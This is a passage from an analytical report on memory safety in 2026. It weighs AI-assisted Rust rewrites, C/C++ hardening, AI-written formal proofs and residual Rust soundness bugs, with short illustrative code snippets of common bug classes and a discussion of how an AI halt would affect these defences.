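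Botmonster Tech's *Big Rust rewrites of 2026* (2026) reports that AI agents ported 535,000 lines of code to Rust in 11 days, or almost 49,000 lines a day. At that speed, ten such efforts could port the 174 million lines of memory-unsafe code that government agencies counted in 172 open-source projects in about a year. This estimate covers only the time needed to write the code. According to the blog, a project also needs good tests before one person with AI agents can port it.

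*Actual curl rewrites in rust* (Stenberg, 2026) makes a similar point about two recent Rust versions of curl, a widely used program for transferring data over the internet. One of them reportedly cost $8,600. Daniel Stenberg, who maintains curl, is impressed by the speed but says that writing code once was never the hard part. AI models had trained on curl's code for years, and the agents could use thousands of existing tests to find their mistakes. Stenberg credits curl's quality to years of decisions and feedback from users. Neglected libraries with few tests often need the most help, but they would be harder to translate well.

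Smith (2026), in *Anthropic's Rust Rewrite Shows Where the Real Work in AI-Driven Migrations Lives*, reports the same difficulty in Anthropic's move of one of its main services from Python to Rust. Generating the code was becoming easier than proving that it worked. Python is already memory-safe, so the aim was not to prevent memory errors.

A rewrite can also introduce new flaws. Botmonster Tech counts 44 security advisories for the Rust versions of Ubuntu's basic command-line tools, none of them for memory bugs. The old C tools had gone through decades of use and repair, and a rewrite starts that process again for every kind of error that Rust does not prevent. Rewriting is probably still worthwhile for a library that has had many memory errors, but it may not be for an old program that has had few and seldom handles untrusted data.

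### A dollar a line

*The Great Refactor* (Bradley and Sastry, 2025), the most ambitious plan for AI rewriting, proposes translating 100 million lines of important open-source code into Rust before 2030 for $100 million. A temporary nonprofit would choose widely used libraries with few maintainers and a history of severe vulnerabilities. One example is Dnsmasq, a network program in many home routers, which had one main maintainer when researchers found several buffer overflows in it in 2017. The summary proposes that the US government provide the full $100 million, but a later passage suggests $50–75 million from the government, with companies contributing 30–40% of the total.

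Only $5 million of the five-year budget, or five cents a line, pays for AI. About $70 million goes to staff, including 15 Rust engineers to check the translations. Each engineer would be responsible for 1.3 million lines a year, or roughly 5,800 every working day. Nobody can review code carefully at that speed, so automatic tests and proofs would have to do nearly all the checking. Giflib still needed corrections by hand, and the plan covers 33,000 times as much code.

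Bradley and Sastry estimate that the project would save $2 billion. They assume that attackers exploit 0.5% of vulnerabilities, that each exploited one costs $4.8 million on average, and that each repair costs $3,000. The expected saving from removing one vulnerability is then

0.005 × $4,800,000 + $3,000 = $27,000

Dividing $2 billion by $27,000 gives about 74,000 memory-safety vulnerabilities. The proposal also assumes that these make up 70% of all vulnerabilities, so the 100 million lines would contain about 106,000 in total. That is roughly one per thousand lines, which is probably the unstated assumption behind the estimate.

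The estimate therefore requires about 740 memory-safety vulnerabilities per million lines, somewhat fewer than the 1,000 that Google reports for Android's C and C++. Google's figure may be several times too high for typical code. The table shows how the savings change with the number of vulnerabilities per million lines.

| Memory-safety vulnerabilities per million lines | Total in 100 million lines | Savings | Savings per dollar spent |
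|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| 1,000 | 100,000 | $2.7 billion | $27 |
| 740 | 74,000 | $2.0 billion | $20 |
| 100 | 10,000 | $270 million | $2.70 |
| 37 | 3,700 | $100 million | $1 |

The project would pay for itself even if the code had only a twentieth as many vulnerabilities as the estimate assumes. But almost 90% of the savings come from the roughly 370 vulnerabilities that attackers would exploit. If attackers exploited 0.1% of the vulnerabilities instead of 0.5%, the savings would shrink from $2 billion to less than $600 million. The calculation also assumes that everyone switches to the new libraries, that the translations add no new vulnerabilities, and that someone would otherwise have found and repaired every old one.

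On the other hand, $4.8 million may be far too low for a vulnerability in a very widely used library. Bradley and Sastry cite an estimate of at least $500 million for cleaning up after Heartbleed, a 2014 memory error in OpenSSL. Preventing a single flaw like that would pay for the project five times over. The savings estimate is rough, but the project would be worth its cost even under quite pessimistic assumptions. The bigger doubt is whether so few people can make sure that 100 million lines of new code work.

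### Getting people to use the new version

A rewritten library protects only those who install it. The quickest way to reach many users is through a Linux distribution, which chooses the default version of each program. In late 2025 Ubuntu made a Rust version of sudo its default, so users got it without having to choose Rust or even know about it. Sudo lets a user run another program with administrator rights, so a flaw in it can give an attacker control of the whole machine. Prossimo (2026), the memory-safety project of the nonprofit Internet Security Research Group, backed the Rust version and says the change improved security for millions of users.

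Even so, the work took years. Prossimo says it was still building its memory-safe tools in 2023 and spent 2024 and 2025 refining them. A model could shorten the building to weeks, but a distribution's maintainers would still need time to find out whether old scripts and unusual settings work with the replacement.

Rustls, a Rust library for encrypted connections, has had a harder time finding adopters. Prossimo has supported it since 2021 and raised well over a million dollars for it. In the Rustls project's own speed tests from March 2026, Rustls came first in 14 of 16 comparisons with OpenSSL and BoringSSL, Google's version of OpenSSL. It also has an OpenSSL-compatible interface. Yet in February 2026 Prossimo was still looking for potential adopters, so speed and safety are evidently not enough to make organisations replace a library that already works.

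Maintainers may also refuse a translation because they do not know Rust. If they keep developing the C version, every new feature and fix has to go into both versions, or the Rust one falls behind. Bradley and Sastry plan for this with five employees to help projects switch and $10 million in grants to maintainers. They also warn that critical infrastructure often runs outdated software because its operators fear breaking something. During a halt, a government could pay for the first few years of maintenance, since a volunteer has little reason to take on a large body of unfamiliar code.

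### What a halt would do to rewriting

If a halt stopped only training, existing models could keep translating code into Rust. They have already translated giflib and Bun, and programmers could still improve the tests, fuzzers and proof tools used with them. The only loss would be the better translations that later models would have produced.

That loss affects the Great Refactor in particular. Bradley and Sastry expect general-purpose models to keep improving, so they advise against spending much on complex tools built for translation. In a halt, the opposite advice would make sense, because progress would have to come from the software around an unchanged model. Programmes like TRACTOR would therefore become more valuable.

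A halt on using AI as well as training it would be much worse, because defenders would lose AI rewriting and AI bug hunting at once, and neither could replace the other. Programmers could still rewrite code by hand, but slowly. The danger is realistic, because Anthropic disabled two models worldwide in June after the US government restricted access. One of them was Fable 5, and Sumner had used a pre-release version of it for Bun.

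A government could exempt translation, though the skills involved are hard to separate from those used in hacking. Carlini and colleagues attribute Mythos Preview's skill at finding vulnerabilities to general gains in coding and reasoning, which good translation also requires. Checking a translation can also expose flaws in the original, as it did with giflib. An approved service could accept C code from a project's maintainers and return Rust with test results, without giving them unrestricted use of the model. The operators would still have to keep any vulnerabilities they found secret until the maintainers had fixed the C version.

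Finished rewrites would remain useful under either kind of halt, because the ordinary Rust compiler checks them, including every later change to their safe code, without an AI model. The best time to translate the most exposed C code is therefore before a halt begins, while the strongest models are still available.

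## Hardening and proving C code that stays in use

Much of the world's C and C++ code will stay in service for years because nobody has the time or money to rewrite it in another language. Engineers can still make it safer by hardening it, which means adding checks that stop the program or disrupt an attack when a memory error occurs, or by using formal verification to prove that certain errors cannot occur. Both methods also work against flaws that nobody has found yet.

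### Bounds checks in the C++ library

C++ programmers often keep data in a `vector`, a type from the language's standard library. A vector stores its own length, but ordinary C++ does not compare an index with that length:

```cpp
std::vector<char> buf(8);
buf[12] = 'x';   // writes outside the buffer
```

With a hardened version of the library, the second line stops the program, much as it would in Rust. Engineers change a compiler setting and rebuild the program without editing the source code.

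Google turned on these checks in Chrome in 2022, using the hardened mode of the libc++ library, and later made them the default on the servers behind Search, Gmail, Maps and YouTube. They slowed its services by 0.30% on average. The slowdown is small partly because the compiler omits unnecessary checks, as it does in Rust. Google's engineers still bypass the checks in a handful of places where speed matters most, and reviewers examine those places carefully.

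The checks have uncovered more than 1,000 bugs, including several that had been in Google's code for over a decade. Google expects them to prevent another 1,000 to 2,000 a year. It does not say how many of these bugs an attacker could have used. Segmentation faults, the crashes that happen when a program tries to use memory it is not allowed to access, fell by 30% across Google's servers. The checks also disrupted one exercise in which Google staff played the attackers, and would have stopped an earlier one. A hardened library is therefore both a defence and a modest way to find bugs without an AI model, because each crash shows engineers where to look.

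The setting protects only C++ code that uses the standard types. C has no such types, so the setting would do nothing for FFmpeg or the Linux kernel, and C++ programs can also use unchecked raw pointers. Google is moving its own C++ to a stricter style called Safe Buffers, in which every buffer access needs a bounds check, but this would not prevent use-after-free errors. In Google's analysis of memory errors that attackers exploited between 2014 and 2023, 40% were out-of-bounds accesses and another 11% could not be classified, so perfect bounds checks would have missed about half or more.

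### Hardened allocators

The allocator is the part of a system that hands out memory when a program calls `malloc` and takes it back after `free`. In the earlier use-after-free example, the attack worked because the second `malloc` returned the cells that the session record had just occupied. A hardened allocator makes this less likely by delaying the reuse of freed memory, placing new blocks at unpredictable positions, or keeping different kinds of data in separate regions. With separate regions, a stranger's message would never land where a session record used to be, although another user's session record still could.

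Some allocators also put inaccessible memory after a buffer so that a long overflow causes a crash, as happened with the flaw in Android's CrabbyAVIF library. Hardened allocators make attacks less reliable but don't rule them out. An overflow that stays within one block goes undetected, and an attacker can make a program request memory repeatedly until it reuses the freed cells.

### Memory tagging and CHERI

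Memory tagging moves part of the checking into the processor. In Arm's version, every 16-byte piece of memory has a tag with one of 16 values, and each pointer carries a tag in bits the address does not need. Most phones use Arm's processor designs. The processor compares the two tags on each access and can stop the program if they differ. When the program frees a block, the allocator changes the block's tag, so old pointers to it should no longer match.

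Suppose a program has an eight-byte buffer and someone sends it 40 bytes. The first 16 bytes land in the buffer's own piece of memory. The last eight of those overflow into unused padding, which the processor does not detect. The 17th byte falls in the next piece, which has a different tag, and the program crashes. Protection against use-after-free depends more on chance. If the allocator picks tags at random, an old pointer still matches one time in 16. An attack that needs two independent matches succeeds one time in 256, and each failure causes a crash that defenders may notice. Attackers can avoid guessing if they can learn the tags beforehand, for example by measuring tiny differences in the processor's timing.

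Google's Pixel phones have supported tagging since the Pixel 8 in 2023, but Google leaves it off for most users. On the iPhone 17, released in 2025, Apple keeps tagging on for the core of the operating system and many system programs. Many other phones lack the feature.

CHERI, a processor design from the University of Cambridge and the research institute SRI International, replaces each pointer with a capability, which holds an address and the limits of the memory the program may reach through it. A hidden bit marks the capability as genuine, and the processor clears that bit if the program tampers with the contents. The processor enforces the limits deterministically, so a capability for an eight-byte buffer cannot reach the ninth byte, whatever the attacker sends. To stop use-after-free as well, the system must search memory for old capabilities to a freed block and cancel them before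 reusing it.

Most C programs need only small changes and a rebuild to run on CHERI, but they also need a new processor. Arm has built a prototype, Morello, and a few companies have designed CHERI chips for small embedded devices. Ordinary phones and PCs do not have CHERI processors.

| Measure | Out-of-bounds access | Use-after-free | Existing devices |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hardened C++ library | Stops it in standard types | No effect | Yes, through an update |
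| Hardened allocator | Catches some cases | Makes attacks less reliable | Yes, through an update |
| Memory tagging | Catches most cases | Catches most cases | Only with a suitable processor |
| CHERI | Stops it | Stops it, with extra software | No |

All four measures leave the flaw in the code. At best they turn a takeover into a crash, which is a minor nuisance in a browser tab. In a program that controls a pump or routes emergency calls, a crash may be what the attacker wants, so someone still has to repair the flaw.

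### How a proof covers every input

A test shows that a program works on the inputs someone tried. A proof can cover all of them. Take the earlier C function that copied a message into an eight-byte buffer, and suppose a programmer has repaired its loop:

```c
for (int i = 0; i < len && i < 8; i++)
    buf[i] = input[i];
```

The counter `i` starts at 0 and only grows, and the loop writes to `buf[i]` only after checking that `i` is below 8. This proves, without running the program, that every write lands inside the buffer, however long the message is.

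The same property can't be proved for the original loop, whose only condition was `i < len`. The proof needs `i` to be below 8, but the condition only guarantees that `i` is below `len`, which the sender chooses. The proof therefore gets stuck at the flaw. A failed attempt can expose a vulnerability in this way, though an attempt may also fail because the prover missed a proof that exists.

Real programs need far longer proofs, and formal verification used to be too expensive for most of them. The best-known success is seL4, the small core of an operating system. A machine-checked proof shows that, for every input, its 8,700 lines of C do exactly what their specification describes. Tolmach and Klaus (2026) note in *The proof is in the spec* that experts spent years on the specification alone.

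### The proofs by Anthropic and Theorem

In October 2026, Anthropic and the startup Theorem published proofs on a much larger scale. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes how Claude proved security properties of compiled code from 123 open-source libraries in a few weeks.

The team started with existing tests from OSS-Fuzz, Google's service for fuzzing open-source software. Each test has an entry point, a small program that takes any string of bytes and passes it to one part of a library. The team turned each test into a formal statement that no input crashes the program, and Claude wrote the proof. Rocq, a mathematical proof checker, then verified every step, so nobody has to read the proofs or trust Claude's reasoning.

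According to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026), Claude's proofs show that, for each of the 239 entry points, the compiled program exits normally on any input under 64 MB, with no crash, memory-safety error or failed assertion (a check the programmers put in the code). The number of possible inputs has more than 150 million digits, so a fuzzer could try only a tiny fraction of them.

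The proofs are about machine code for RISC-V, an open processor design with a fairly simple set of instructions. The team modelled the processor, the relevant behaviour of Linux and a fixed amount of memory. Each program runs as a single thread, doing one thing at a time, and has its libraries built in. Compilers have bugs, and a proof about machine code, unlike one about C, does not depend on the compiler being correct. This approach also works for any language and requires no rewriting.

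The proofs are very long. The parser in cJSON, a C library for the common text format JSON, has 391 lines of C, and its proof has about 630,000 lines, or roughly 1,600 for each line of C. That is not unusual for the project. OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) reports about 600,000 lines for a program of 18,000 instructions and 180 million lines in total, though another account puts the total at a billion. At cJSON's ratio, proofs for the 174 million memory-unsafe lines that government agencies counted in 172 projects would run to about 280 billion lines. A computer checks the proofs, so length alone is no obstacle, but somebody has to pay for an AI model to write them.

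Failed proofs exposed hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed, and Claude wrote repairs for them. One was a buffer overflow (CVE-2026-56132) in libexpat, a widely used library for reading XML files, and others were logic errors. Some of the proofs therefore apply only to the repaired code, and users of older versions do not get the guarantee. Claude also failed to prove some of the targets. Anthropic is publishing the specifications for those, along with the proofs for programs that needed no changes, so that others can check the work.

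A smaller project found flaws in a similar way. Andrews and Zhang (2026), in *Formalizing CPython*, had Claude Opus 5.5 translate parts of CPython, the C program that runs most Python code, into Lean and prove properties of the translation. The work had covered 16% of CPython by November and led to 418 bug reports. About 55 of those bugs let ordinary Python code crash CPython or corrupt its memory.

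### What the proofs leave out

A proof covers only the stated property. A JSON parser that exited immediately without reading anything would satisfy the no-crash property, and so would a login program that accepted every password. According to Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026), logic flaws of that kind rarely cause failures that automatic tools can detect. Stronger properties can be proved. In the same project, Claude proved that the Linux kernel's code for zlib, a compressed data format, follows the published standard, but few programs have a standard that precise.

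The 239 proofs also cover only the entry points that people had written for fuzzing. In 2024 Google found a vulnerability in a cJSON function with an AI-written fuzz test, which called the function in a way that the existing human-written test did not. A proof based on the human-written test would cover every input to that test, but perhaps not every way another program might call the function.

The modelled computer differs from those most people use. Most people run these libraries on x86 processors, found in most PCs and servers, or on Arm, in programs that load a C library called glibc at startup. The RISC-V programs instead had musl, a simpler C library, built in. *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) shows how much harder the usual setting is to verify. On RISC-V, musl's function for comparing two pieces of text has 14 instructions. On the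 x86 processor that Leip's team chose, glibc's version has 316 instructions, 45 of them jumps.

A flaw in the C source will often exist on every processor, so the RISC-V proofs are still good evidence about other machines, though they do not prove anything about them. According to OpenNET, the proofs also leave out threads, separately loaded libraries and faulty hardware. The omission of threads matters most for security, because browsers and operating systems do many things at once, and one thread may free memory that another is still using. The proofs therefore do not yet cover some of the most dangerous memory errors in the most exposed software.

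Other teams began to close the gap within weeks. Leip's team at the security company Zellic, working with V12, proved a security property of a complete Linux program on x86 with glibc built in. The proof assumes one particular processor and does not rule out a crash during glibc's start-up, before the program's own code begins. In *AlphaProof Code* (2026), Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues went further on Arm, using AI agents that wrote 6.5 million lines of proof about the machine code of libsignal, which encrypts messages for the app Signal. The proofs show, among other things, that messages stay secret and that users can tell who sent them, which no memory-safe language can check. They cover a test program for two-person conversations, not the whole library (EconoTimes, *Google DeepMind Uses AlphaProof Code to Verify a Compiled Signal Harness*, 2026).

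Every proof also relies on parts that nobody has proved. For libsignal these come to about 26,000 lines, including the description of the Arm processor. If that description is wrong, a correct proof can lead to a false conclusion. Keles (2026), in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, considers the trusted part of binary proofs still huge, because the models of the processor and of Linux both need checking. He points out that even seL4 had bugs, and wants people to name the exact properties proved instead of calling software "formally verified". *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug*, a post on kirancodes.me, describes fuzzing a version of zlib that had a machine-checked proof. This exposed a buffer overflow in the Lean runtime, the supporting code that the program needed to run, which the proof did not cover. Proofs about whole compiled programs can avoid this gap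 because they include the supporting code.

AI adds the risk of proofs that are correct but worthless. When Andrews and Zhang first asked their agents to prove something about every function, fewer than half of the functions they reviewed passed. A typical proof showed that if a function returns a number, the number is at least zero, which is also true of a function that always crashes. For each proof, they now ask whether a broken version of the function could also pass.

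An impossible assumption is harder to spot. Tolmach and Klaus describe an AI system that had to translate into Lean the deliberately false statement that if 3^x = 5, then 3^(x+2) = 51 (the correct value is 45). The system declared x to be a whole number, and since no whole number satisfies 3^x = 5, Lean would accept a proof of the false statement. Someone could similarly "prove" a parser safe by assuming a condition that no input can meet. Anthropic and Theorem reduced this risk by deriving their statements from existing fuzz tests, but most software has no such tests.

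### Hardening and proof during a halt

Hardening could continue under either kind of halt, because it needs no AI model. A government that wanted quick results could start with hardened libraries and allocators, which reach existing devices through ordinary updates. But Google needed more than a year of testing before it turned on the library checks everywhere, and a company with fewer engineers might need longer. Devices whose makers have stopped sending updates would not receive these protections.

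Memory tagging spreads only as people buy new devices. If no phones had tagging at first, owners replaced a random quarter of all phones each year, and every new phone had tagging switched on, the share with tagging would be 25% after one year, 58% after three and 76% after five. The replacement rate is invented. Actual progress would probably be slower because many new phones do not have tagging. Industrial equipment can stay in place for decades. CHERI would hardly matter in a five-year halt except in new embedded devices.

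Formal verification depends much more on the type of halt. If only training stopped, existing models could keep writing proofs. Opus 5.5, which did the work on CPython, is already commercially available, and people could improve the processor models and reusable proof libraries used with it. Zellic and V12 began their x86 project in mid-September and published a proof by the end of October. Much of their work can be reused for other programs, so each new proof should take less work even if the AI model never improves.

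A halt on AI use would slow verification to roughly the pace of seL4, which required years of expert work for a few thousand lines of code. Governments could exempt verification, but this would in effect exempt a form of AI bug hunting, because a model's failed attempt to prove a program safe often reveals a vulnerability. Operators of the exempted models, like those of an approved translation service, would have to keep these vulnerabilities secret until maintainers had fixed them.

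Existing proofs would remain valid, and anyone could check them again without AI. But a proof about machine code applies to only one compiled program. When maintainers add a feature, fix a logic flaw or switch compilers, the instructions change, and at least part of the proof needs redoing. Without AI models, maintainers would often have to choose between an old version with a proof and a new version without one. Hardened libraries do not have this problem, because every rebuild includes their checks.

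## Memory errors that survive in memory-safe languages

A program in a memory-safe language can still contain memory errors, because the compiler's guarantee depends on code that the compiler cannot fully check. A Rust program may contain unsafe code or use packages that do. It also calls Rust's standard library, the basic functions that come with the language, and many of these use unsafe code. The compiler itself has bugs, so it sometimes accepts code it should reject. In 2026, AI bug hunting found errors in all of these places.

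An attacker can reach some of these errors just by sending data to a program or renting space on the same computer. Others do harm only if a programmer writes very unusual code, perhaps on purpose.

### A flaw in a virtual machine monitor

Cloud companies often run virtual machines for several customers on one physical computer, and those customers have no reason to trust each other. A program called a virtual machine monitor keeps the virtual machines isolated from one another. Since any customer might be an attacker, a monitor is an obvious candidate for a memory-safe language.

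Carlini and colleagues reported in April that Mythos Preview had found an out-of-bounds write in such a monitor, which was already in production use. Like the overflow in Android's CrabbyAVIF library, the flaw is in unsafe code. A monitor cannot avoid unsafe code entirely, because hardware works with raw memory addresses. Suppose the system inside a virtual machine, known as the guest, asks the monitor to store one byte in the guest's memory:

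```rust
// base: where the guest's memory starts on the physical computer
// offset: a position chosen by the guest
unsafe { *base.add(offset) = byte; }
```

The compiler has no information about the size of the guest's memory, so the programmer has to compare `offset` with that size first. If this check is missing or wrong, a malicious guest can write to the monitor's memory. The real flaw may be more complicated than this example, but it had the same effect.

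An outside attacker could plausibly reach this flaw, since anyone can rent a virtual machine. Carlini and colleagues say it is easy to use for a denial-of-service attack on the physical computer, which could also interrupt other customers' work. Mythos Preview could not build an exploit that did more than this, though the flaw might serve as one step in a longer attack. The model's failure is only weak reassurance, because stronger models have appeared since.

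The flaw had no patch in April, so Carlini and colleagues withheld the project's name and published only a hash of the details. It may be the Firecracker flaw on Anthropic's later public list.

Other memory-safe languages have similar gaps. Java programs can handle raw pointers through a rarely used class, `sun.misc.Unsafe`, or call C code through a more common interface. Python's `ctypes` module gives direct access to memory.

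### Unsafe code behind safe functions

Many Rust programmers never write `unsafe` themselves but use packages that contain it. A package often wraps an old C library in functions that look like ordinary safe Rust. Such a function is "sound" if no program written entirely in safe Rust can cause undefined behaviour through it. Undefined behaviour is a breach of the language's basic rules, such as reading freed memory, after which the program may do anything.

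Momeu and Sen (2026), in *Agentic Discovery of Soundness Bugs in Safe Rust Bindings*, give an example from `ssh2`, a package for encrypted connections to other computers. One of its functions asks a server how a user may log in:

```rust
let ann = session.auth_methods("ann")?;
let bob = session.auth_methods("bob")?;   // frees Ann's answer
println!("{ann}");                        // reads freed memory
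```

The underlying C library keeps only the latest answer and frees the previous one. The Rust function's signature does not express this rule, so the compiler accepts the program. If the function had required an exclusive reference to `session`, the compiler would have rejected the second call while the program still needed Ann's answer. Returning a copy of the answer would also have prevented the error.

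In 2021 a team led by Yechan Bae ran an analysis tool named Rudra on 43,000 Rust packages. In six and a half hours it found 264 previously unknown memory-safety bugs, according to Georgia Tech's *New Bugs Identified in Popular Programming Language*. This doubled the number of known memory-safety bugs in Rust. Rudra did not need an AI model, but it could detect only three patterns that the team had identified beforehand.

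*UnsafeChecker* (2026) describes a newer search of the whole Rust package registry. The researchers found 114 bugs in 83 packages and confirmed them with Miri, a tool that runs Rust code and reports undefined behaviour. Many of the bugs were in basic packages for data structures and memory management. Developers or experts from RustSec, which collects Rust security advisories, have acknowledged 45 of the bugs, and developers have fixed 27.

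AI agents can look for errors that fit no known pattern. Momeu and Sen had agents audit 19 widely used packages, most of them wrappers around C and C++ libraries. The agents found 213 cases of undefined behaviour, or about 11 per package. Rudra had found one bug per 163 packages, but it searched the whole registry, while Momeu and Sen chose packages likely to have such errors. Their agents also found 11 cases of undefined behaviour in the Linux kernel's Rust code.

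Most of these bugs are probably much less dangerous than the flaw in the virtual machine monitor. A function is unsound if some safe program could misuse it, even if no such program exists. To benefit from the `ssh2` bug, an attacker would need a real program that makes a second call and then uses the first answer. Some bugs are in code that handles untrusted data, such as the use-after-free errors that maintainers fixed in the `openssl` package's certificate checks, which programs use on certificates from strangers. But the count of 213 does not show how many of the bugs an outsider could exploit in existing software.

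### The standard library

Rust's standard library has about 34,000 functions. In *Verifying the Rust Standard Library*, Cook, Delmas and colleagues (2026) count roughly 7,500 unsafe functions and 3,000 safe ones that use unsafe code internally, together almost a third of the total. A growable list, for example, has to reserve raw memory and track which part holds valid data. Developers reported more than 74 soundness bugs in the library over three years, but it has received only 18 CVE records in its history.

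Bae now works at Microsoft's FORGE Lab, where researchers searched the Rust standard library with an AI-powered scanner named Hyenas. On November 9, Bae (2026), in *Memory Safety Bugs in Rust Standard Library*, reported several memory-safety bugs, including some that entirely safe Rust code can trigger. Bae traces them to three mistaken assumptions in unsafe code: that other code will not panic, that code supplied by the library's users is correct, and that the underlying system behaves as expected.

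Panics are dangerous because a Rust program normally runs clean-up code for its remaining values before it stops. Suppose a function empties a list of five items by freeing them one by one and then setting the list's length to zero. If the third item's clean-up code panics, the function never resets the length. Because the length is still five, the list's own clean-up code then frees the first two items again. An attacker can sometimes exploit such a double free to corrupt memory. Setting the length to zero before freeing anything prevents this. A panic might then leave some memory unfreed, which is wasteful but safe. RustSec's *Advisories with keyword 'memory-safety'* lists at least four packages with memory errors caused by panicking clean-up code, all from two days in September 2026.

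Code supplied by a library's users can cause similar problems. A library function might call a method on a programmer's own data type to get the number of items to expect, reserve memory for that many, and write the items without further checks. If the method returns 10 but the type produces 12 items, the last two are written outside the reserved memory. The programmer made a mistake, but a wrong number from safe Rust code should never corrupt memory, so the library's unsafe code is at fault for relying on it.

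Errors can also arise where the library meets the operating system. For example, the library might ask the system to fill a 64-byte buffer, and the system might report that it wrote 100 bytes. If the library accepts that number, later code may read past the end of the buffer. Bae writes that bugs at this boundary can now be found. The other two kinds are more familiar, since Rudra already checked for them in 2021, but they still occur five years later.

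An outside attacker usually cannot choose a program's data types or make the operating system return false results. Most of these bugs would therefore matter only in a program that already has another fault, such as clean-up code that panics on certain inputs. But nearly every Rust program uses the standard library, so a few programs may well meet the conditions. Rust normally compiles the library into each program, so a fix reaches users only after developers rebuild their programs and users install the new versions.

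Since November 2024 the Rust Foundation has run a contest that pays people to prove parts of Rust's standard library free of undefined behaviour. Contributors wrote 725 proof set-ups by hand in the first 15 months. A tool then generated 16,748 automatically, each of which calls one function with all possible inputs at once. Kani, an automatic proof tool, confirmed 11,970 of them, covering about 35% of the library's functions. The others failed because of time limits, unsupported features or missing descriptions of code that the functions call.

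These proofs vary in strength. Cook and colleagues think the best are for 989 functions that have a formal statement of what they require and guarantee. Kani does not check for data races, in which two threads use the same memory at once without coordination, or for violations of Rust's rules on overlapping references. The generator also skipped 9,635 generic functions, which work with many types of data.

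*Verifying the Rust Standard Library* reports that the verification effort uncovered no previously unknown memory-safety vulnerability. This is good evidence about the functions it covered. It does not contradict Bae's later findings, because the automatic proofs left out generic functions, and user-supplied code mostly enters the library through those.

### The compiler

Anthropic's Frontier Red Team asked Claude to prove that safe Rust is type-safe, meaning it never treats one type of data as another. When part of a proof failed, Claude looked for a program that broke the rule. The same method found flaws in a Linux component that checks small programs before they run in the kernel. Anthropic published the work on December 2, 2026.

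*Claude Found a Seven-Year Bug in the Rust Compiler* (Faisal, 2026) describes a five-line program in safe Rust that reads freed memory. The program has an array inside another array, and the inner one owns a number stored in separately reserved memory. To make a reference to an element, the program first works out a position in each array. While working out the second position, it moves the inner array away and frees it. The borrow checker, the part of the compiler that enforces the rules on references, does not connect this step with the new reference, so the program ends up with a reference to freed memory. Miri confirms the use-after-free.

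Rust developers traced the bug to April 2019, when a test version of the compiler switched to more flexible rules for references. Anthropic's Nicholas Carlini, who is not a Rust expert, had people who knew the language check the example before he reported it on August 4. The bug was still open in early December, though a contributor was working on a fix. Claude found several dozen such problems, and Rust's maintainers have around 178 similar issues open.

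An attacker who can only send data to a finished program cannot add this expression to its code. A programmer would have to write it, and few would free an array while looking up a position inside it. Anthropic describes the findings as bugs rather than security vulnerabilities in the usual sense, although the example could hide a vulnerability in code that looks safe.

In October a developer known as jsnell reported an even older bug, in *struct's lifetime requirements can be bypassed via covariant field assignment*. A Rust type can require that any reference inside it remain valid for as long as the program runs. The compiler should reject a shorter-lived reference in such a type, but it sometimes accepts one. If the type's clean-up code saves that reference elsewhere, the program can use it after the memory it points to is no longer valid. Owen (2026), in *What the 11-year-old Rust borrow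 checker bug means*, notes that the Rust project gave the bug high priority but not the highest. It had gone unnoticed for 11 years, and exploiting it requires deliberately malicious clean-up code.

Compiler bugs that let safe Rust break memory safety matter most to services that compile and run strangers' code. If a service relies on the absence of `unsafe` to protect other users' memory, an attacker can deliberately write the contrived program that triggers the bug. A malicious contributor could also use a compiler bug to hide a vulnerability from reviewers who read only unsafe code. But safe Rust can already delete files or send passwords over the network, so a malicious contributor seldom needs a compiler bug to do damage.

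### How far the search can be narrowed

Almost all known memory errors in Rust involve unsafe code. *Building Sound Evaluation Practices for Rust-Based Security Frameworks* (2026) mentions at least 230 recorded memory-safety bugs in unsafe code, and cites research in which every vulnerability studied required unsafe code. The exceptions are compiler bugs, which the Rust project can look for in one place for all Rust programmers.

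Reviewers must still read more than the unsafe blocks. Suppose a list stores its length as an ordinary number, and an unsafe block reads that many items. If a safe function in the same file sets the length too high, the unsafe block reads past the end of the list, even though its own code has not changed. For a wrapper such as `ssh2`, reviewers must also read the C library to learn the rules for using it. That library can have memory errors of its own, which even a correct wrapper would not fix.

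Vander Stoep puts the unsafe share of Android's Rust code at about 4%. If reviewers had to read four more lines for each unsafe one, which is a guess, they could still skip 80% of the Rust code when looking for memory errors.

The search is also cheap, with a median cost of less than $50 per package in Momeu and Sen's audits. In separate test audits, another AI model classified only one of 838 findings as false, but the agents often missed bugs. Those tests found 51 distinct defects that were not already public, and 15 of them appeared in only one audit, so repeating audits is worthwhile. At $50 per audit, auditing each of 1,000 important packages three times would cost $150,000, excluding the cost of checking the findings and repairing the code.

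Fixing the bugs again takes longer than finding them. Maintainers have fixed 24 of the 78 findings that Momeu and Sen reported, or 31%. After 71 reports from another AI-assisted search of Rust packages, which Openwall (2026) published in August, maintainers had fixed or otherwise settled 33 issues, not all of them memory errors. Both rates are well above the 12% for Anthropic's open-source reports, although the numbers are small and the projects differ. Rust maintainers might therefore keep up with a moderate flow of reports.

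A training-only halt would hardly hinder this kind of search. Momeu and Sen compared Claude Opus 5.5 with DeepSeek V4.1 Flash, an open model. With full instructions, each found 25 or 26 defects that were not yet public, and DeepSeek cost a quarter as much per defect. If a halt also restricted the use of models, defenders who obeyed it would lose these audits, while attackers could keep running copies of open models they already had.

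Defenders would still have Rudra, Miri and fuzzing, which don't need an AI model. These tools can search large amounts of Rust code, but they would often miss errors like the one in `ssh2`, because the rule it breaks appears only in the C library. Human experts would have to check the most exposed wrappers by hand, which is more realistic for a limited amount of unsafe code than for a whole C program.

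## Flaws that memory safety does not remove

A program with no memory errors can still let a stranger log in, show one customer another's invoices or run an attacker's commands. Across software as a whole, flaws other than memory errors make up much more than 30% of serious vulnerabilities, although people often put the share of memory errors at about 70%.

### Where the 70% figure comes from

The 70% figure comes mainly from two sources. In 2019 Matt Miller, a security engineer at Microsoft, showed that memory errors had made up about 70% of the vulnerabilities the company fixed each year since 2006. In 2020 the Chromium project examined 912 high- or critical-severity security bugs since 2015 and found about the same share. Roughly half of Chromium's memory errors were use-after-free bugs.

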